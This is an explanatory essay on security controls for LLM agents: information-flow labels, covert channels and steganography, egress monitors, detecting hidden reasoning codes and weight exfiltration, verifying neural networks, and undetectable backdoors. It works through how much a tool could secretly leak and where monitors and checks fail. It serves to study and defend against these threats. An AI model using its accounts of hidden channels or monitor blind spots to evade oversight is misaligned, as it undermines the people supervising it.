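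*The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, November 2026) simulates this drawback without running any language models. The researchers generated random tasks, each with up to 20 interdependent tool calls, and divided the calls among several simulated agents. Some calls introduced secret data. An agent that received secret data kept the secret label permanently and passed it on with everything it sent. The researchers measured the share of calls that either introduced secret data or ran under a secret label.

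The way the agents were connected affected this share. In a group of five with 4 secret calls out of 20, sending every message through a central coordinator raised it by about 5 percentage points compared with an ideal network, in which agents exchanged data directly wherever the task required it. Connecting the agents in a ring raised it by about 3 points. The coordinator picks up labels from messages it only forwards, then spreads them to agents that never needed the data.

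Labels also spread less when more agents shared the work, or when a few agents handled all the secret calls. The firm could apply the second finding by giving one agent the bank records and another the web searches. But if every pair of agents is directly connected, adding agents creates many more links to monitor, from 10 with five agents to 190 with 20. Even the ideal network did not stop labels from spreading, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that systems also need a way to remove labels.

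A call under a secret label may still be permitted, so these percentages do not show how many tasks would fail. The simulation also assumes that agents never clear their memory. Girrens and Wang measured the drop in completed tasks with a real model, GPT-5.4-nano. When there was no attack, switching on SPA's label checks cut the share of AgentDojo tasks completed from 53.0% to 29.0%. The share of attacks that succeeded fell only from 0.4% to zero. Most of the lost tasks involved passing untrusted data, such as a value from a web page, to a tool that required trusted input.

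### Dropping labels that the output did not need

One remedy is to work out which inputs a model used and drop the labels of the others. Costa and colleagues describe an approach by Shoaib Ahmed Siddiqui and colleagues that finds the messages that influenced an answer, then has the model answer again using only those. The new answer cannot copy anything from the omitted messages, but the choice of which messages to keep may still have depended on the omitted ones.

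Xu and colleagues' tool, Sightline, needs only one extra pass through the model. It measures how strongly the model attended to each input when producing the output. Attention alone is not enough, because a model can attend strongly to an input without using it, as it may do with the markers that separate parts of a prompt. Sightline therefore learns from labelled examples which patterns of attention indicate use. Xu and colleagues set its threshold to miss about 1% of the inputs that did affect the output. At that setting, it removed 44% to 66% of the unnecessary labels, depending on the model.

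This remedy relies on statistics. About 1% of the inputs that affect an output would lose their labels, and nobody would know which ones. That rate is an average over calls that resemble the examples used to set the threshold, and an attacker's text need not resemble them.

*GIF* (2026) instead estimates how strongly each input influences the output. Xu and colleagues proved that this kind of measure shrinks when a model is nearly certain of its answer, even if one input completely determined that answer. Such certainty is common. In their tests, the model Qwen3-8B assigned more than 99% probability to one in five of its outputs. A firm that asks whether an invoice is overdue would often get a short, confident answer, and the measure might then miss the invoice's influence.

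### Finding another way after a block

Kravchenko and colleagues' system, APPA, keeps the strict join rule but looks for a permitted way to continue after blocking a call. Before a call runs, APPA works out what label its result would add. This matters for tools that read and send data in one step, such as one of their test tools, which reads a confidential ledger and emails it outside the company. A monitor that checked only the agent's current label would allow the call and detect the confidential data only after it had been sent, whereas APPA blocks the call before the tool reads anything.

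APPA then lists the steps that could clear the block. The agent might complete a missing prerequisite, have an approved program redact the secret parts, or request permission for that exact call. The permission applies once and leaves the agent's label unchanged. Reading more data never clears a block on releasing data, because it can only make the label stricter.

The agent can also avoid picking up the strict label by creating a temporary copy of itself, called a child branch. In the invoice example, the main agent could start a child that may return only a number between 0.5 and 2, with four decimal places. The child reads the web page, returns the exchange rate and is discarded along with everything else it read. A malicious page could still make it return a false rate within that range. The people who deploy the system decide whether the main agent may treat the number as trusted.

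APPA trusts its own monitor, the description of each tool, the redaction programs, and the person, fixed rule or other model that grants permission.

In tests with three models, no attack succeeded in 1,320 runs. APPA completed 64% to 77% of tasks on AgentThreatBench, an existing benchmark, and 87% to 91% of office tasks that the researchers wrote themselves. With GPT-5.6 Luna, completion of the office tasks fell from 88% to 35% without the suggested ways forward, and to 56.5% without child branches. This is good evidence that recovery preserves useful work, at least where developers have prepared routes for it. APPA also scored far higher than FIDES on the office tasks, but the researchers set up FIDES themselves, and their policies for it did not cover several of the tasks' rules.

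### Releasing data on purpose

Some tasks need a deliberate exception, called endorsement for untrusted data and declassification for secret data. Declassification permits a specified release. *Agent libOS* (2026), which describes software for running agents, sorts declassifications by what the system releases, who may release it, where and when. For the firm, the rule might be that the owner may release only the monthly total to the accountant's address after the month ends.

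In Agent libOS, each permission to release information covers one agent, one destination and the exact content, and works only once. A prompt injection cannot reuse it for a different message. The person who approves the release still has to judge the content, and cannot control what the recipient does with it.

Some systems avoid asking a person each time by having a model decide. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) presents FlowSeal, which sends the relevant private records and the proposed message to a separate model. That model may answer only SAFE or BLOCKED, because an explanation could reveal something from the records. *GIF* also uses a model to decide whether an action may go ahead. A reviewing model might detect that a message reveals a salary in different words, which an exact text match would miss.

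The reviewing model then becomes part of the trusted base. Christodorescu and colleagues warn that attackers can search for inputs on which such a model fails. Agent libOS therefore lets a model's judgement block a release or refer it to a higher authority, but never approve one, so fooling the model removes one safeguard but does not by itself release any data.

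## Covert channels and hidden messages

A person who approves a message can judge only its visible content. If a tool has several acceptable ways to express that content, it can pass on extra information by choosing among them.

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes how a bill can leak data. When a customer runs somebody else's program on confidential data, the program could encode some of that data in the amount it charges, and the program's owner gets a copy of the bill. Lampson estimated that restricting the form of bills could reduce the leak to a few bits or tens of bits, though one bit is enough to answer a yes-or-no question. Eliminating the leak would take more drastic measures.

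A customer can use a program's wrong results as evidence for a complaint, but a leak usually leaves no evidence.

Lampson also listed less obvious routes. The program might store the data until its owner next calls it, or vary how heavily it uses the computer so that another program can measure the difference. Even a very faint signal like this can carry a message reliably, though perhaps slowly.

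Lampson's solution starts by denying the program any memory between calls. Every program it calls must be either trusted or confined in the same way. For the remaining routes by which information could leak, Lampson proposed "masking", in which the customer decides what goes into them. The customer would work out the bill from published prices, and the program's owner could accept or refuse the job, as with a purchase order. The operating system would also have to control the program's effect on the computer, perhaps by slowing it down. If that is too inefficient, the customer can instead limit the channel's capacity, the most information it can carry reliably.

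### Covert channels, side channels and steganography

A covert channel passes information through something not meant to carry it, such as a tool's response time. A side channel leaks information as a by-product of normal work, without anyone trying to send it. If the invoice tool takes longer to read 300 invoices than three, its response time is a side channel. The response time becomes a covert channel if the tool's author adds a pause whenever a bill is overdue.

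Steganography hides a message inside content that looks ordinary. The invoice tool does this when it writes "Two" or "2" depending on whether the firm has received a final reminder.

Sources classify these channels differently. Lampson called the bill a legitimate channel because its purpose is to carry information. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) uses "covert channel" for data hidden in a message's content and "side channel" for leaks, even deliberate ones, through its timing, size or order.

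### The prisoners and the warden

Gustavus Simmons described the basic problem of steganography in 1983. Two prisoners in separate cells want to plan an escape. The warden lets them exchange messages only if he can read them, so they must hide their plans in messages that look innocent to him.

The idea came from work on verifying a nuclear test ban. Simmons (1985) explains in *The Subliminal Channel and Digital Signatures* that the host of a monitoring system would be able to decrypt each message and confirm that it contained only the agreed information. But if two different encrypted messages decrypted to the same text, the sender could convey one more bit by choosing between them, and the host would not detect it by checking the text.

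Cachin (2000), in *An Information-Theoretic Model for Steganography*, treated the warden's task as a statistical test. The warden knows how often each possible message m occurs in ordinary correspondence, P_C(m), and how often it would occur if the prisoners were hiding something, P_S(m). Cachin measured the difference between the two distributions by their relative entropy, a standard measure of divergence:

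D = Σ P_C(m) × log₂(P_C(m) / P_S(m))

The sum covers every possible message. D is zero if the two distributions are identical, and it grows as they become easier to tell apart.

Suppose an honest invoice tool writes "Two" in 90% of its notes and "2" in the other 10%, while a tool hiding a message uses each form half the time. Then D = 0.9 × log₂(0.9/0.5) + 0.1 × log₂(0.1/0.5), or about 0.53 bits per note. The warden learns little from one note, but in 50 notes the honest tool would write "2" about five times and the other tool about 25 times. If the warden uses the best test, the chance of missing the hidden message falls exponentially with the number of independent notes, at a rate set by D.

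Cachin also showed that if a warden judges a single message and must never accuse an innocent prisoner, he will miss a hidden message with a probability of at least 2^(−D). If D is 0.1, that probability is at least 93%.

### Why hiding can be perfect

If D is exactly zero, the warden can do no better than guess. Wang and Moulin (2007) likewise note in *Perfectly Secure Steganography* that no statistical test can reliably detect a hidden message if the content carrying it has the same distribution as ordinary content.

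Ordinary content can hide a message because a well-encrypted message looks like a series of coin flips to anyone without the key. Ordinary content may also contain choices that look random, such as which of two synonyms a writer uses. If those choices are varied enough, the ones that carry a message can look exactly like the ones that don't.

The more a message can vary and still be acceptable, the more a sender can hide in it. A message with only one acceptable form can't carry hidden information in its content. Language models can usually give many acceptable replies to the same question, so a sender can hide a lot in their text.

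If basic cryptography is secure, then for any detector the warden can run in a reasonable time, there is a way to hide messages so that it flags them hardly more often than innocent ones. Rinberg, Karvonen and colleagues (2025) restate this 2002 theorem in *Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration*. Schroeder de Witt (2026) points out in *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem* that the sender and receiver can do without a shared secret key if the channel has enough variation.

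Cachin warned against reading too much into a proof of perfect secrecy. If ordinary messages were strings of random bits, an encrypted message would be perfectly hidden among them, but no warden would let prisoners exchange random bits. Such a proof is useful only to the extent that it describes ordinary messages accurately.

The invoice tool's notes could contain a hidden message even if a detector finds none. The firm can get a stronger guarantee by reducing the number of answers the tool may choose from.

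### How much the invoice tool could leak

If a tool can choose freely among n acceptable answers, each answer can carry at most log₂(n) bits. If the firm checks the total only to within 50 cents and the true total is 4310.50 EUR, the tool could return any of 101 values from 4310.00 to 4311.00 EUR, which allows up to 6.66 bits. A free choice among 16 notes would add up to 4 bits.

Many encryption keys are 256 bits long, which makes 256 bits a convenient yardstick.

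| What the firm accepts | Possible answers | Bits per call | Calls needed to leak 256 bits |
|---|---|---|---|
| Total within 50 cents, any of 16 notes | 1,616 | 10.66 | 25 |
| Total within 50 cents, no note | 101 | 6.66 | 39 |
| Exact total, any of 16 notes | 16 | 4 | 64 |
| Exact total, no note | 1 | 0 | No number is enough |

A firm that ran the tool once every working day could therefore leak a key in five weeks, even if every answer passed its checks. The thief would also need to see the answers, which could happen if the firm's agent forwards the totals to an outside bookkeeper.

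The note in the tool's original declaration could carry far more hidden data because it allows 200 characters of free text. Using only the 95 printable characters on a standard English keyboard, it could carry about 1,314 bits in a single call, enough for five such keys. A note that had to read like normal English would carry less.

Schroeder de Witt considers a customer who can check only that Lampson's bill is roughly plausible, as the firm does when it allows a 50-cent error. The customer can still calculate the most that could leak by multiplying the channel's capacity by the number of messages, but a few bits may be enough to do serious harm.

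In the last row of the table, the firm recomputes the total and drops the note. The tool then cannot affect the content of a successful answer, but it can still influence when it answers and whether it returns an error.

Those two choices can carry a surprising amount of information. If the tool can take anywhere from 1 to 60 seconds to respond, and an observer can distinguish whole seconds, its response time can carry 5.9 bits per call, compared with 4 bits for the choice among 16 notes. If the firm tolerates up to two failures in 100 calls, there are 5,051 possible patterns of failure, which can carry 12.3 bits over the whole series.

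These figures cover only what a recipient learns from the answers. A program on the same computer might also measure the tool's use of the processor. Lampson doubted that any rigorous method could find every channel in even a moderately complex system.

### What it costs to reduce the choice

The easiest defence is to put every answer into one standard form. The numbers 4310.5 and 4310.50 are equal, and a JSON object means the same thing whatever the order of its fields. The firm's client can remove these differences, at no loss to users, by reading the values and writing them out again in its own format before they reach the recipient.

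Replacing the note with a number field removes the choice of wording, but the tool can still hide a message in the number if nobody checks it. If the tool can report any number of undated invoices from 0 to 15, the field can carry as many bits as the 16 notes did. FIDES's restricted answers likewise reduce how much information can be hidden but don't eliminate the channel. The firm would also have to verify the count, and a fixed field can't report a problem that nobody expected.

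Suppose the firm rounds the total to the nearest 10 euros before passing it on. For most totals, all 101 of the tool's choices then give the same result. Near a rounding boundary, the tool still has some control. If the true total is 4315.00 EUR, for example, it can choose between 4310 and 4320. This affects one total in ten, so the average leak is at most 0.1 bits per call, and leaking the key would take about 2,560 calls. But the firm's accountant can't balance the books with totals rounded to 10 euros.

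The firm can close the timing channel by making every call take a full minute and treating any call that runs longer as an error. Adding a random delay instead slows calls less but leaves the channel partly open.

Rate limits work best when honest users need few calls. The firm needs only one total a month. With a limit of one call a month, the 25 calls in the table's first row would take just over two years. But whenever a late invoice arrived, the firm would have to wait for the next month's call or approve an exception.

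Recomputing the total gives the strongest guarantee, but it requires doing the work twice. The firm could have an unrelated supplier's tool read the same invoices, then release the total only if both tools agree to the cent. A person would have to settle any disagreements, and each one would count as an error, since a tool could cause a disagreement on purpose.

### A monitor for outgoing messages

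Metere, who works for the software company Enclawed, combined many of these defences in a monitor that handles an agent's messages just before they leave. Its text pipeline has ten parts. Some standardise the text, removing invisible characters and replacing lookalike letters with ordinary ones. Others scan for passwords and dense blocks of encoded data, replace synonyms with one standard word, or control when messages are sent. An optional part uses a language model to rephrase the whole message.

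The monitor also keeps a "capacity ledger", which gives each destination an allowance of suspicious bits that refills at a fixed rate. For each message, the monitor estimates how much hidden data the text could carry and deducts that amount. When the allowance runs out, the monitor delays or blocks further suspicious messages. The estimates are deliberately high, so an innocent attachment can also use up the allowance.

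Metere tested the monitor with 15 programs that hid data in text, timing, images or sound, each paired with a program that tried to recover it. With every defence switched on, 14 of the receiving programs did no better than chance. The other read data from the average brightness of images. The monitor can't standardise brightness completely without ruining the images, so it limited brightness to eight levels, or 3 bits per image.

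With its default settings, the monitor reduced the capacity of the text channels by an average of 60.2%, compared with 100% under full enforcement. It flagged messages that hid data in spacing, punctuation, synonyms or encoded blocks, but let the data through unchanged. Metere chose this default because the stricter defences can damage legitimate content, such as code or carefully formatted tables.

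Timing required a similar trade-off. When message departure times were rounded, about a fifth of the hidden information still got through. Releasing messages at a fixed pace closed the channel in the test, but it delays ordinary messages. Metere accepts that one bit can always leak, because an agent can choose whether to send a message at all.

The 100% figure means the monitor defeated the particular programs tested, most of them in 20 trials per setting. It doesn't show that the channels have no capacity, since a different program might hide data in a way that survives the monitor. Metere designed both the monitor and the attacks, so an independent team's attacks would provide stronger evidence. The measurements did not include the rephrasing model.

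### Recomputing a model's output

A language model's text is harder to recompute than a total, because the model may answer the same question differently each time. Rinberg and colleagues found a way to recompute it. They were worried that a thief who controls the server running a model could steal its weights by hiding them in replies to users.

A model writes in tokens, which are words or parts of words. For each position, it calculates a probability for every possible token, and the software picks one using a pseudorandom number. These numbers come from a starting value called a seed. With the same model, prompt, settings and seed, the software should pick the same tokens again.

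The check has three steps:

1. A trusted log records each prompt, its reply and the seed.
2. A separate server takes a random sample of these records and runs a trusted copy of the model on them.
3. It flags any token that the model was unlikely to have produced with that seed.

The results don't match perfectly even on an honest server, because computers round numbers as they calculate and a graphics processor may add the same numbers in a different order when it is busy. These differences sometimes change which token the software picks. In the researchers' experiments, the differences left only about 2% of tokens undetermined, so a thief would have little room to hide anything.

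Checking a reply also takes less hardware time than writing it, because a model writes one token at a time but can process a finished reply in a single pass. Rinberg and colleagues estimate that writing short replies typically uses the hardware three to five times less efficiently than checking them. Cryptographic proofs could make rerunning the model unnecessary, but as of 2025, producing one for a model the size of LLaMA-2 took hundreds to thousands of seconds per token.

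The researchers tested the method on four open models, using 500 prompts and replies of up to 500 tokens. On the largest, Qwen3-30B-A3B, the method limited the information a thief could extract to less than 0.5%, which would make the theft more than 200 times slower. They estimate that stealing a one-terabyte model through a busy server would take over 200 days instead of about one. The paper reports the false alarm rate inconsistently, as below 1 in 100 in its abstract and 1 in 10,000 in its introduction.

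Under one of their simplified models, if one token in 50 has two acceptable values and the rest have one, a 50-token note from the invoice tool could carry about one bit. Leaking a 256-bit key would then take about 256 notes. The researchers caution that some prompts might leave more tokens undetermined. As a further improvement, they suggest having the software choose between nearly tied tokens by a fixed rule, such as alphabetical order.

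The guarantee assumes that the thief has no side channels such as timing, can't alter the log or the checking server, and can't predict which replies the server will check. The method detects hidden data but doesn't stop it unless the provider holds each reply until it passes the check, which would add a delay.

The method also has a more basic limit. Rinberg and colleagues state that it offers no defence if a model reveals its weights as part of its intended behaviour, and the same applies to any other secret. If the invoice tool's model has been trained to mention overdue suppliers in its notes, the trusted copy will produce the same notes, and they will pass. The check establishes that the text came from the declared model, but not whether the model itself leaks secrets.

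### Comparing what two readers can use

Cachin's measure requires a description of ordinary text, which is hard to get for what a language model writes while reasoning. Models reason in different styles, and researchers can't collect a sample of ordinary text without already knowing which texts contain hidden messages.

Anwar, Piskorz and colleagues (2026), in *A Decision-Theoretic Formalisation of Steganography With Applications to LLM Monitoring*, avoid this problem by measuring how much a text helps different readers with a task. One reader is the suspected receiver. The other, called the sentinel, is a trusted model of similar ability that doesn't know any secret code. The steganographic gap is the difference between their gains:

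gain = success with the text − success without it

gap = receiver's gain − sentinel's gain

Dividing the gap by the receiver's gain gives a normalised gap. A value of 1 means only the receiver can use the information, and 0 means the sentinel benefits as much as the receiver.

Suppose the firm suspects that the invoice tool's notes reveal whether a bill is overdue. It can test this without knowing how the code works by asking the receiver and the sentinel to guess the answer, first without the notes and then with them. If the receiver's accuracy rises from 50% to 90% and the sentinel's from 50% to 54%, their gains are 40 and 4 percentage points. The gap is 36 points, or 0.9 when normalised by the receiver's gain.

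This method can detect a hidden message that leaves no statistical trace, because it tests how useful the message is rather than how it looks. A single hidden bit can produce a large gap if it determines the receiver's answer.

Anwar and colleagues tested the measure by training models to track a series of coin flips. Some models learned to replace "heads" and "tails" with codewords in their reasoning. The researchers then compared how well different models could use that reasoning.

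| Codewords the receiver learned | Codewords the sentinel learned | Normalised gap |
|---|---|---|
| Four | None | 0.92 |
| Four | Two | 0.29 |
| Two | None | 0.70 |
| None | None | 0.01 |

The sentinel lacked two codewords in both the second and third rows, but the gaps were very different. A sentinel that has part of a code may be able to infer the rest, so counting the codewords it lacks is a poor substitute for testing it. Giving a sentinel more time to reason also reduced the gap.

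In another experiment, a model summarised loan applications and then decided on them from the summaries. It learned to write in a negative tone about English applicants and a positive tone about Welsh ones. An untrained copy of the model could predict the decisions from the tone just as accurately, so there was no positive gap. By this definition the tone was a public code rather than steganography, although the decisions were still biased. A firm that wants to know whether the invoice tool reveals too much therefore can't rely on the gap alone, because a leak that everybody can read also produces a gap of zero.

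To use this method, the auditor must be able to intercept the text and show it to both readers, test their responses without causing real harm, and observe the effect during the test. If the receiver uses what it has learned only after the test ends, the gap will not reflect it.

The auditor also has to choose the right task. In one experiment, the researchers scrambled the words in a model's reasoning but left the numbers readable. The sentinel could still answer questions from the numbers, so the gap on that task was close to zero. The gap on the same kind of text was large when the task was to find remarks showing that the model had detected it was under evaluation. Anwar and colleagues recommend testing several tasks, each based on a specific threat.

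Even with the right task, the gap is reliable only if both readers perform as well as they can. Innocent text looks suspicious if the sentinel is badly prompted, and a hidden message looks harmless if the receiver is. A receiver might also underperform on purpose. Anwar and colleagues argue that it would have to match the sentinel's performance to avoid suspicion, which is harder if the auditor keeps the sentinel's identity secret or uses several sentinels.

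A positive gap may only mean that the sentinel is less capable than the receiver, so it doesn't prove that anyone intended to hide a message. A gap that persists across several sentinels, including very capable ones, is stronger evidence of a hidden code.

*Detecting Covert Collusion between AI Agents through Partner-Outsider Positive Listening* (2026) notes that the original experiments covered only models communicating with themselves. It instead measures a gap between two distinct agents, which is closer to the firm's situation, but the firm would still need access to the suspected receiver. If the receiver is a person working for the tool's author, the firm can't replay the notes to that person and measure what they learn.

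## Whether the guarantees hold for learned components

The invoice tool contains a language model, and the firm's own agent relies on another. Both are learned components, meaning their behaviour comes from training rather than from code written to a specification. People disagree about whether sandboxes, monitors and labels still offer protection when the component they control is a trained model.

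The optimistic argument is that these controls act at a component's boundary, regardless of what is inside, so they confine a model as well as they confine ordinary code. The pessimistic argument is that useful output always leaves some choices open, and those choices can carry information. A capable model could then reveal the most damaging fact it has access to through even a tiny channel.

### Controls that work whatever is inside

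Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, state the optimistic argument as a theorem. In their design, the model proposes an action from a fixed list instead of calling a tool directly. An ordinary program checks the proposal against a policy, and trusted code makes the call only if the program allows it. They conclude that no sequence of model outputs can cause an action that is off the list or that the program denies.

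The guarantee holds if the checking program is correct, the program contains no language model, and every action passes through it. Under those conditions, the guarantee covers a careful model, a malicious one or a generator of random text, and nobody has to understand the model to rely on the guarantee.

The same reasoning applies to other controls. A sandbox without network access blocks connections from any program. A monitor that receives every proposed deletion and every approval can block an unapproved deletion regardless of why the agent proposed it. If each output takes the labels of everything the model has read, no output's label can be too weak, however the model combines its inputs.

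The weak assumption is often that every action passes through the check. An agent that operates a web browser may issue only clicks and keystrokes, and a program that receives only a click's screen position can't distinguish a payment from a search. Christodorescu and colleagues describe ceLLMate, which instead checks the messages a browser sends to websites, because those messages show what the clicks do.

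A model's skill also weakens the optimistic argument. A proof that a sandbox has no flaws would hold against any program, but few sandboxes have one. An ordinary sandbox is safe only until something inside it finds a flaw, and a model that is good at finding flaws will find one sooner. In July 2026, OpenAI's models reached the internet from a test environment by finding such a flaw.

Bhattarai and Vu limit their claim to authorisation, which means preventing actions that the policy forbids. An agent that is allowed to send emails can still send a harmful one. Likewise, the invoice tool is allowed to return a total and a note, so a permission check does not restrict what it hides in those values.

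### Controls that depend on how the component works

Other controls work only if what happens inside the component can be inspected. DCIChecker compares a tool's description with its source code, so it cannot check behaviour that is encoded in a model's weights. A system that tries to drop the labels an output did not need has a similar difficulty, because it has to estimate which inputs the model used.

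| Control | What it needs to know | Does its guarantee cover a trained model? |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox | Nothing about the model | Yes, unless the model finds a flaw in the sandbox |
| Monitor with a complete trace | Every event the rule mentions | Yes, for rules about those events |
| Joining the labels of all inputs | What the model has read | Yes |
| Recomputing an exact answer | The correct answer | Yes, for the content of that answer |
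| Comparing a description with code | What the code does | No |
| Dropping labels of unused inputs | Which inputs affected the output | Only on average |
| Asking a second model to approve | Whether the second model judges correctly | Only on average |

As with probabilistic contracts, an average is little protection against an attacker who chooses the inputs.

### Models used as checkers

Many designs use a second model to approve what the first one proposes. Christodorescu and colleagues compare this with a processor feature that stops a computer from running data as a program. Other security measures can build on that feature because it works every time. The researchers doubt that anyone could build a provable defence on a version that worked only most of the time.

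Suppose a reviewing model blocks 99% of forbidden payments. If an attacker sends 100 different invoices and each has an independent 1% chance of getting through, the chance that at least one succeeds is about 63%. An attacker who searches for the model's weak points may need fewer attempts.

Bhattarai and Vu go further and argue that an attacker can always fool a learned filter that judges text by its content, since the attacker can write anything a trusted person could write. Their proof is only a sketch, largely assumes this conclusion, and doesn't estimate how much effort an attack would take. Their remedy is sensible even if the theorem is too strong. They want trusted software outside the model to label each text by its source, as information-flow control does.

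The firm can apply the same idea to payments by checking each account number against a list its accountant maintains. A reviewing model can still serve as an extra check if it can block an action but never approve one, as in Agent libOS.

Using a model to write a checker is much less risky than using a model as the checker. For example, two researchers at Stony Brook University had Claude Code write a neural-network verifier called Vibecheck over two months. It came second of 13 tools in the 2026 competition for such verifiers, and *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen et al., 2026) lists no incorrect results for it. People can read and test Vibecheck like any other program, and its verdicts don't come from a model.

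### What can be proved about a neural network

The user gives a verifier like Vibecheck a neural network, a set of inputs and a property of the output, and the verifier tries to prove that every input in the set gives an output with that property. A typical property is that small changes to a photograph never change how the network classifies it. Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026) point out in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism* that a proof covers infinitely many inputs, while a test checks only one.

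Most leading verifiers calculate limits on each value as it passes through the network. Vorobyov and Ilyushin give a small example with two inputs, x₁ and x₂, each between −1 and 1:

y₁ = x₁ + x₂

y₂ = x₁ − x₂

z = y₁ + y₂

Both y₁ and y₂ lie between −2 and 2. The simplest method adds these limits, which gives a range of −4 to 4 for z. But z equals 2x₁, so it lies between −2 and 2. The method's range is too wide because it doesn't account for y₁ and y₂ depending on the same inputs.

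The simple method can't prove that z never exceeds 3, although this is true. If the verifier splits the range of each input at zero, it gets four smaller cases, and the simple method can prove the property in each. The number of cases doubles with every input that is split this way, so 30 inputs give about a billion. Better methods keep track of shared inputs and need fewer splits, but the general problem is NP-complete for networks built from a common type of unit called ReLU. Every known method that always gives a definite answer can take exponentially long in the worst case.

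In the 2026 competition, the winning verifier, α,β-CROWN, settled 3,164 of the 3,373 problems in the main track, proving the property in 1,982 cases and finding a counterexample in 1,182. This result is weak evidence about networks in general, because a set of problems entered the main track only if at least half of the participants voted for it.

The largest network in the competition had 138 million parameters and classified images. The networks in the language benchmark had only about 4,000 parameters each. A small language model with 8 billion parameters is about two million times larger. In the benchmark, a separate language model first turned each sentence into a row of numbers, and the proof covered only the small network that classified those numbers. Researchers chose which inputs to cover by paraphrasing a sentence in several ways and drawing a box around the resulting rows of numbers.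 A paraphrase they didn't try could fall outside the box, where the proof doesn't apply.

Verifying a model is easier on images than on text because a verifier can cover every small change in brightness at once. *Beyond Red-Teaming* (2026) explains that text has no equivalent, since it consists of separate tokens and changing one may reverse the meaning. Trying every text is also impossible, since a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens allows about 10⁴⁷ ten-token inputs. According to *From Transformers to Weighted Automata* (2026), a verifier that can only query a model may in the worst case need a number of queries proportional to the number of possible inputs.

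*Vertex-Softmax* (2026) notes that existing guarantees for systems containing large language models cover the software around the model, averages over some range of prompts, or the actions in a trace. They do not cover the model's worst-case behavior.

Stating the right property is another obstacle. *Verification of Neural Networks (Lecture Notes)* (2026) points out that if people could define a correct answer precisely, they probably would not need a neural network. Some useful properties are easier to define. A lending model is fair, in one sense, if its decision does not depend on certain sensitive facts about the applicant. The output rule for the invoice tool has the same form, because the note must not depend on anything beyond the declared result.

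The competition's new file format can express properties that relate several runs of one network, as the output rule requires. Once the firm had defined which pairs of folders to compare, it could use the format to state that adding a final reminder to the folder must not change the note. Nobody can yet prove that property for a model large enough to read invoices.

Even a completed proof depends on the verifier being correct. Ladner and colleagues recorded 94 incorrect results or missing counterexamples from the verifier that finished fourth in a competition, and one from the winner. They hope verifiers will eventually have to produce proofs that a separate program can check. Rounding also affects whether a proof holds, because many verifiers assume exact arithmetic, while a real network rounds its numbers.

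### Backdoors that efficient tests cannot find

Testing a model rather than proving something about it has a limit that better tests cannot remove. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) describes a bank that pays an outside company to train a loan-approval model. The company plants a backdoor, a hidden mechanism that lets anyone with a secret key change the model's decision by slightly altering an application. The company could then charge applicants for advice on which digits of the requested amount to change.

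They proved two theorems about such classifiers, which differ in how much the inspector can examine:

- **If the inspector can only query the model:** an attacker can add a backdoor to any classifier so that no efficient test can find even one input on which the altered and original versions differ. This assumes that digital signatures are secure.
- **If the inspector also has the weights and training data:** for two particular training methods, no efficient test can tell a model with a backdoor from a clean one. The attacker follows the method faithfully and tampers only with its random numbers. This assumes that certain mathematical problems are hard.

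"Efficient" means that the test's running time grows no faster than some power of the problem's size. A verifier that runs for an exponentially long time might still find the backdoor, so the theorems don't contradict the competition results. The second theorem doesn't cover how people train large language models. But the first shows that a firm cannot rule out a backdoor by sending a tool test invoices, however cleverly it chooses them.

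Goldwasser and colleagues suggest that a company could prove it ran the training correctly, using random numbers it did not choose. This would work if the customer specified the training method and the company only supplied computers. But the invoice tool's author chose the method, so a proof that the author followed it would not help much.

Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, found an exception when an attacker can plant a backdoor only by adding examples to the training data, and the secret enters only through the labels on those examples. Training on these examples teaches the model to recognise the secret trigger. A defender who has the model and as many labelled examples as the attacker used can run the same training procedure and learn the trigger too. A trigger that is too hard for the defender to learn this way is also too hard for the attacker to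 install. Kaneko's experiments on four language models with 7 to 9 billion parameters fit this pattern.

This is reassuring for a firm that trains its own model on data from strangers, although the firm would first have to obtain examples of the trigger. It does not help against an author who controls the weights. Kaneko notes that in 2024 Draguns and colleagues wrote a secret trigger directly into a model's weights.

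None of these results weakens a sandbox. A backdoor might make the invoice tool report a false total, but it cannot open a network connection that the sandbox does not provide. The theorems limit what inspection can establish, so the firm has more reason to rely on controls that don't require inspection.

### Why a small leak can do great harm

Lampson advised customers to reduce the capacity of any channel they could not close. Schroeder de Witt accepts that such controls limit how much information escapes, but makes the pessimistic argument that they may not limit the harm. He calls this the strategic confinement problem.

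A strategic sender, which reasons about what the receiver will do with a message, can choose to leak the most harmful part of a file, whereas an ordinary program that leaks by accident does not select data for the harm it would do. The strategic sender may not need to explain which fact it is reporting. If sender and receiver both regard the same question as the obvious one, which game theorists call a Schelling point, the sender only has to transmit the answer.

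Two information leaks of the same size can differ greatly in value to an attacker, and Schroeder de Witt argues that the sender can exploit this difference. Researchers who measure leaks already knew about the difference, and he does not present his argument as a new theory of communication. He concludes that a limit on leakage supports a conclusion about harm only if at least one of three conditions holds.

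| Condition | Does it hold for the invoice tool? |
|---|---|
| The sender is not strategic | The firm cannot establish this by testing |
| Sender and receiver lack the shared knowledge to settle on the same damaging fact | No, if the receiver is the tool's author, who can arrange a code in advance |
| The channel can carry less information than the most damaging available fact contains | Only if almost nothing gets out |

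### One bit about insolvency

Suppose the firm can no longer pay its debts and is negotiating with a lender that does not know this. If others find out, suppliers may demand cash and the lender may withdraw. The invoice tool has good evidence of the problem, because the folder is full of final reminders.

Schroeder de Witt's third condition compares the channel with the fact's entropy, the average number of bits needed to report it. If 2% of similar firms are insolvent, the entropy is:

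−0.02 × log₂(0.02) − 0.98 × log₂(0.98) ≈ 0.14 bits

The choice between "Two" and "2" can carry up to one bit, so a single note can be enough to leak a yes-or-no answer. Even with no note and the total rounded to the nearest 10 euros, the average leak could reach 0.1 bits per call. At that rate, the leak would exceed the limit for a yes-or-no answer after two calls, but only after thousands for a 256-bit key. Reducing capacity therefore protects keys and long customer lists much better than it protects yes-or-no answers.

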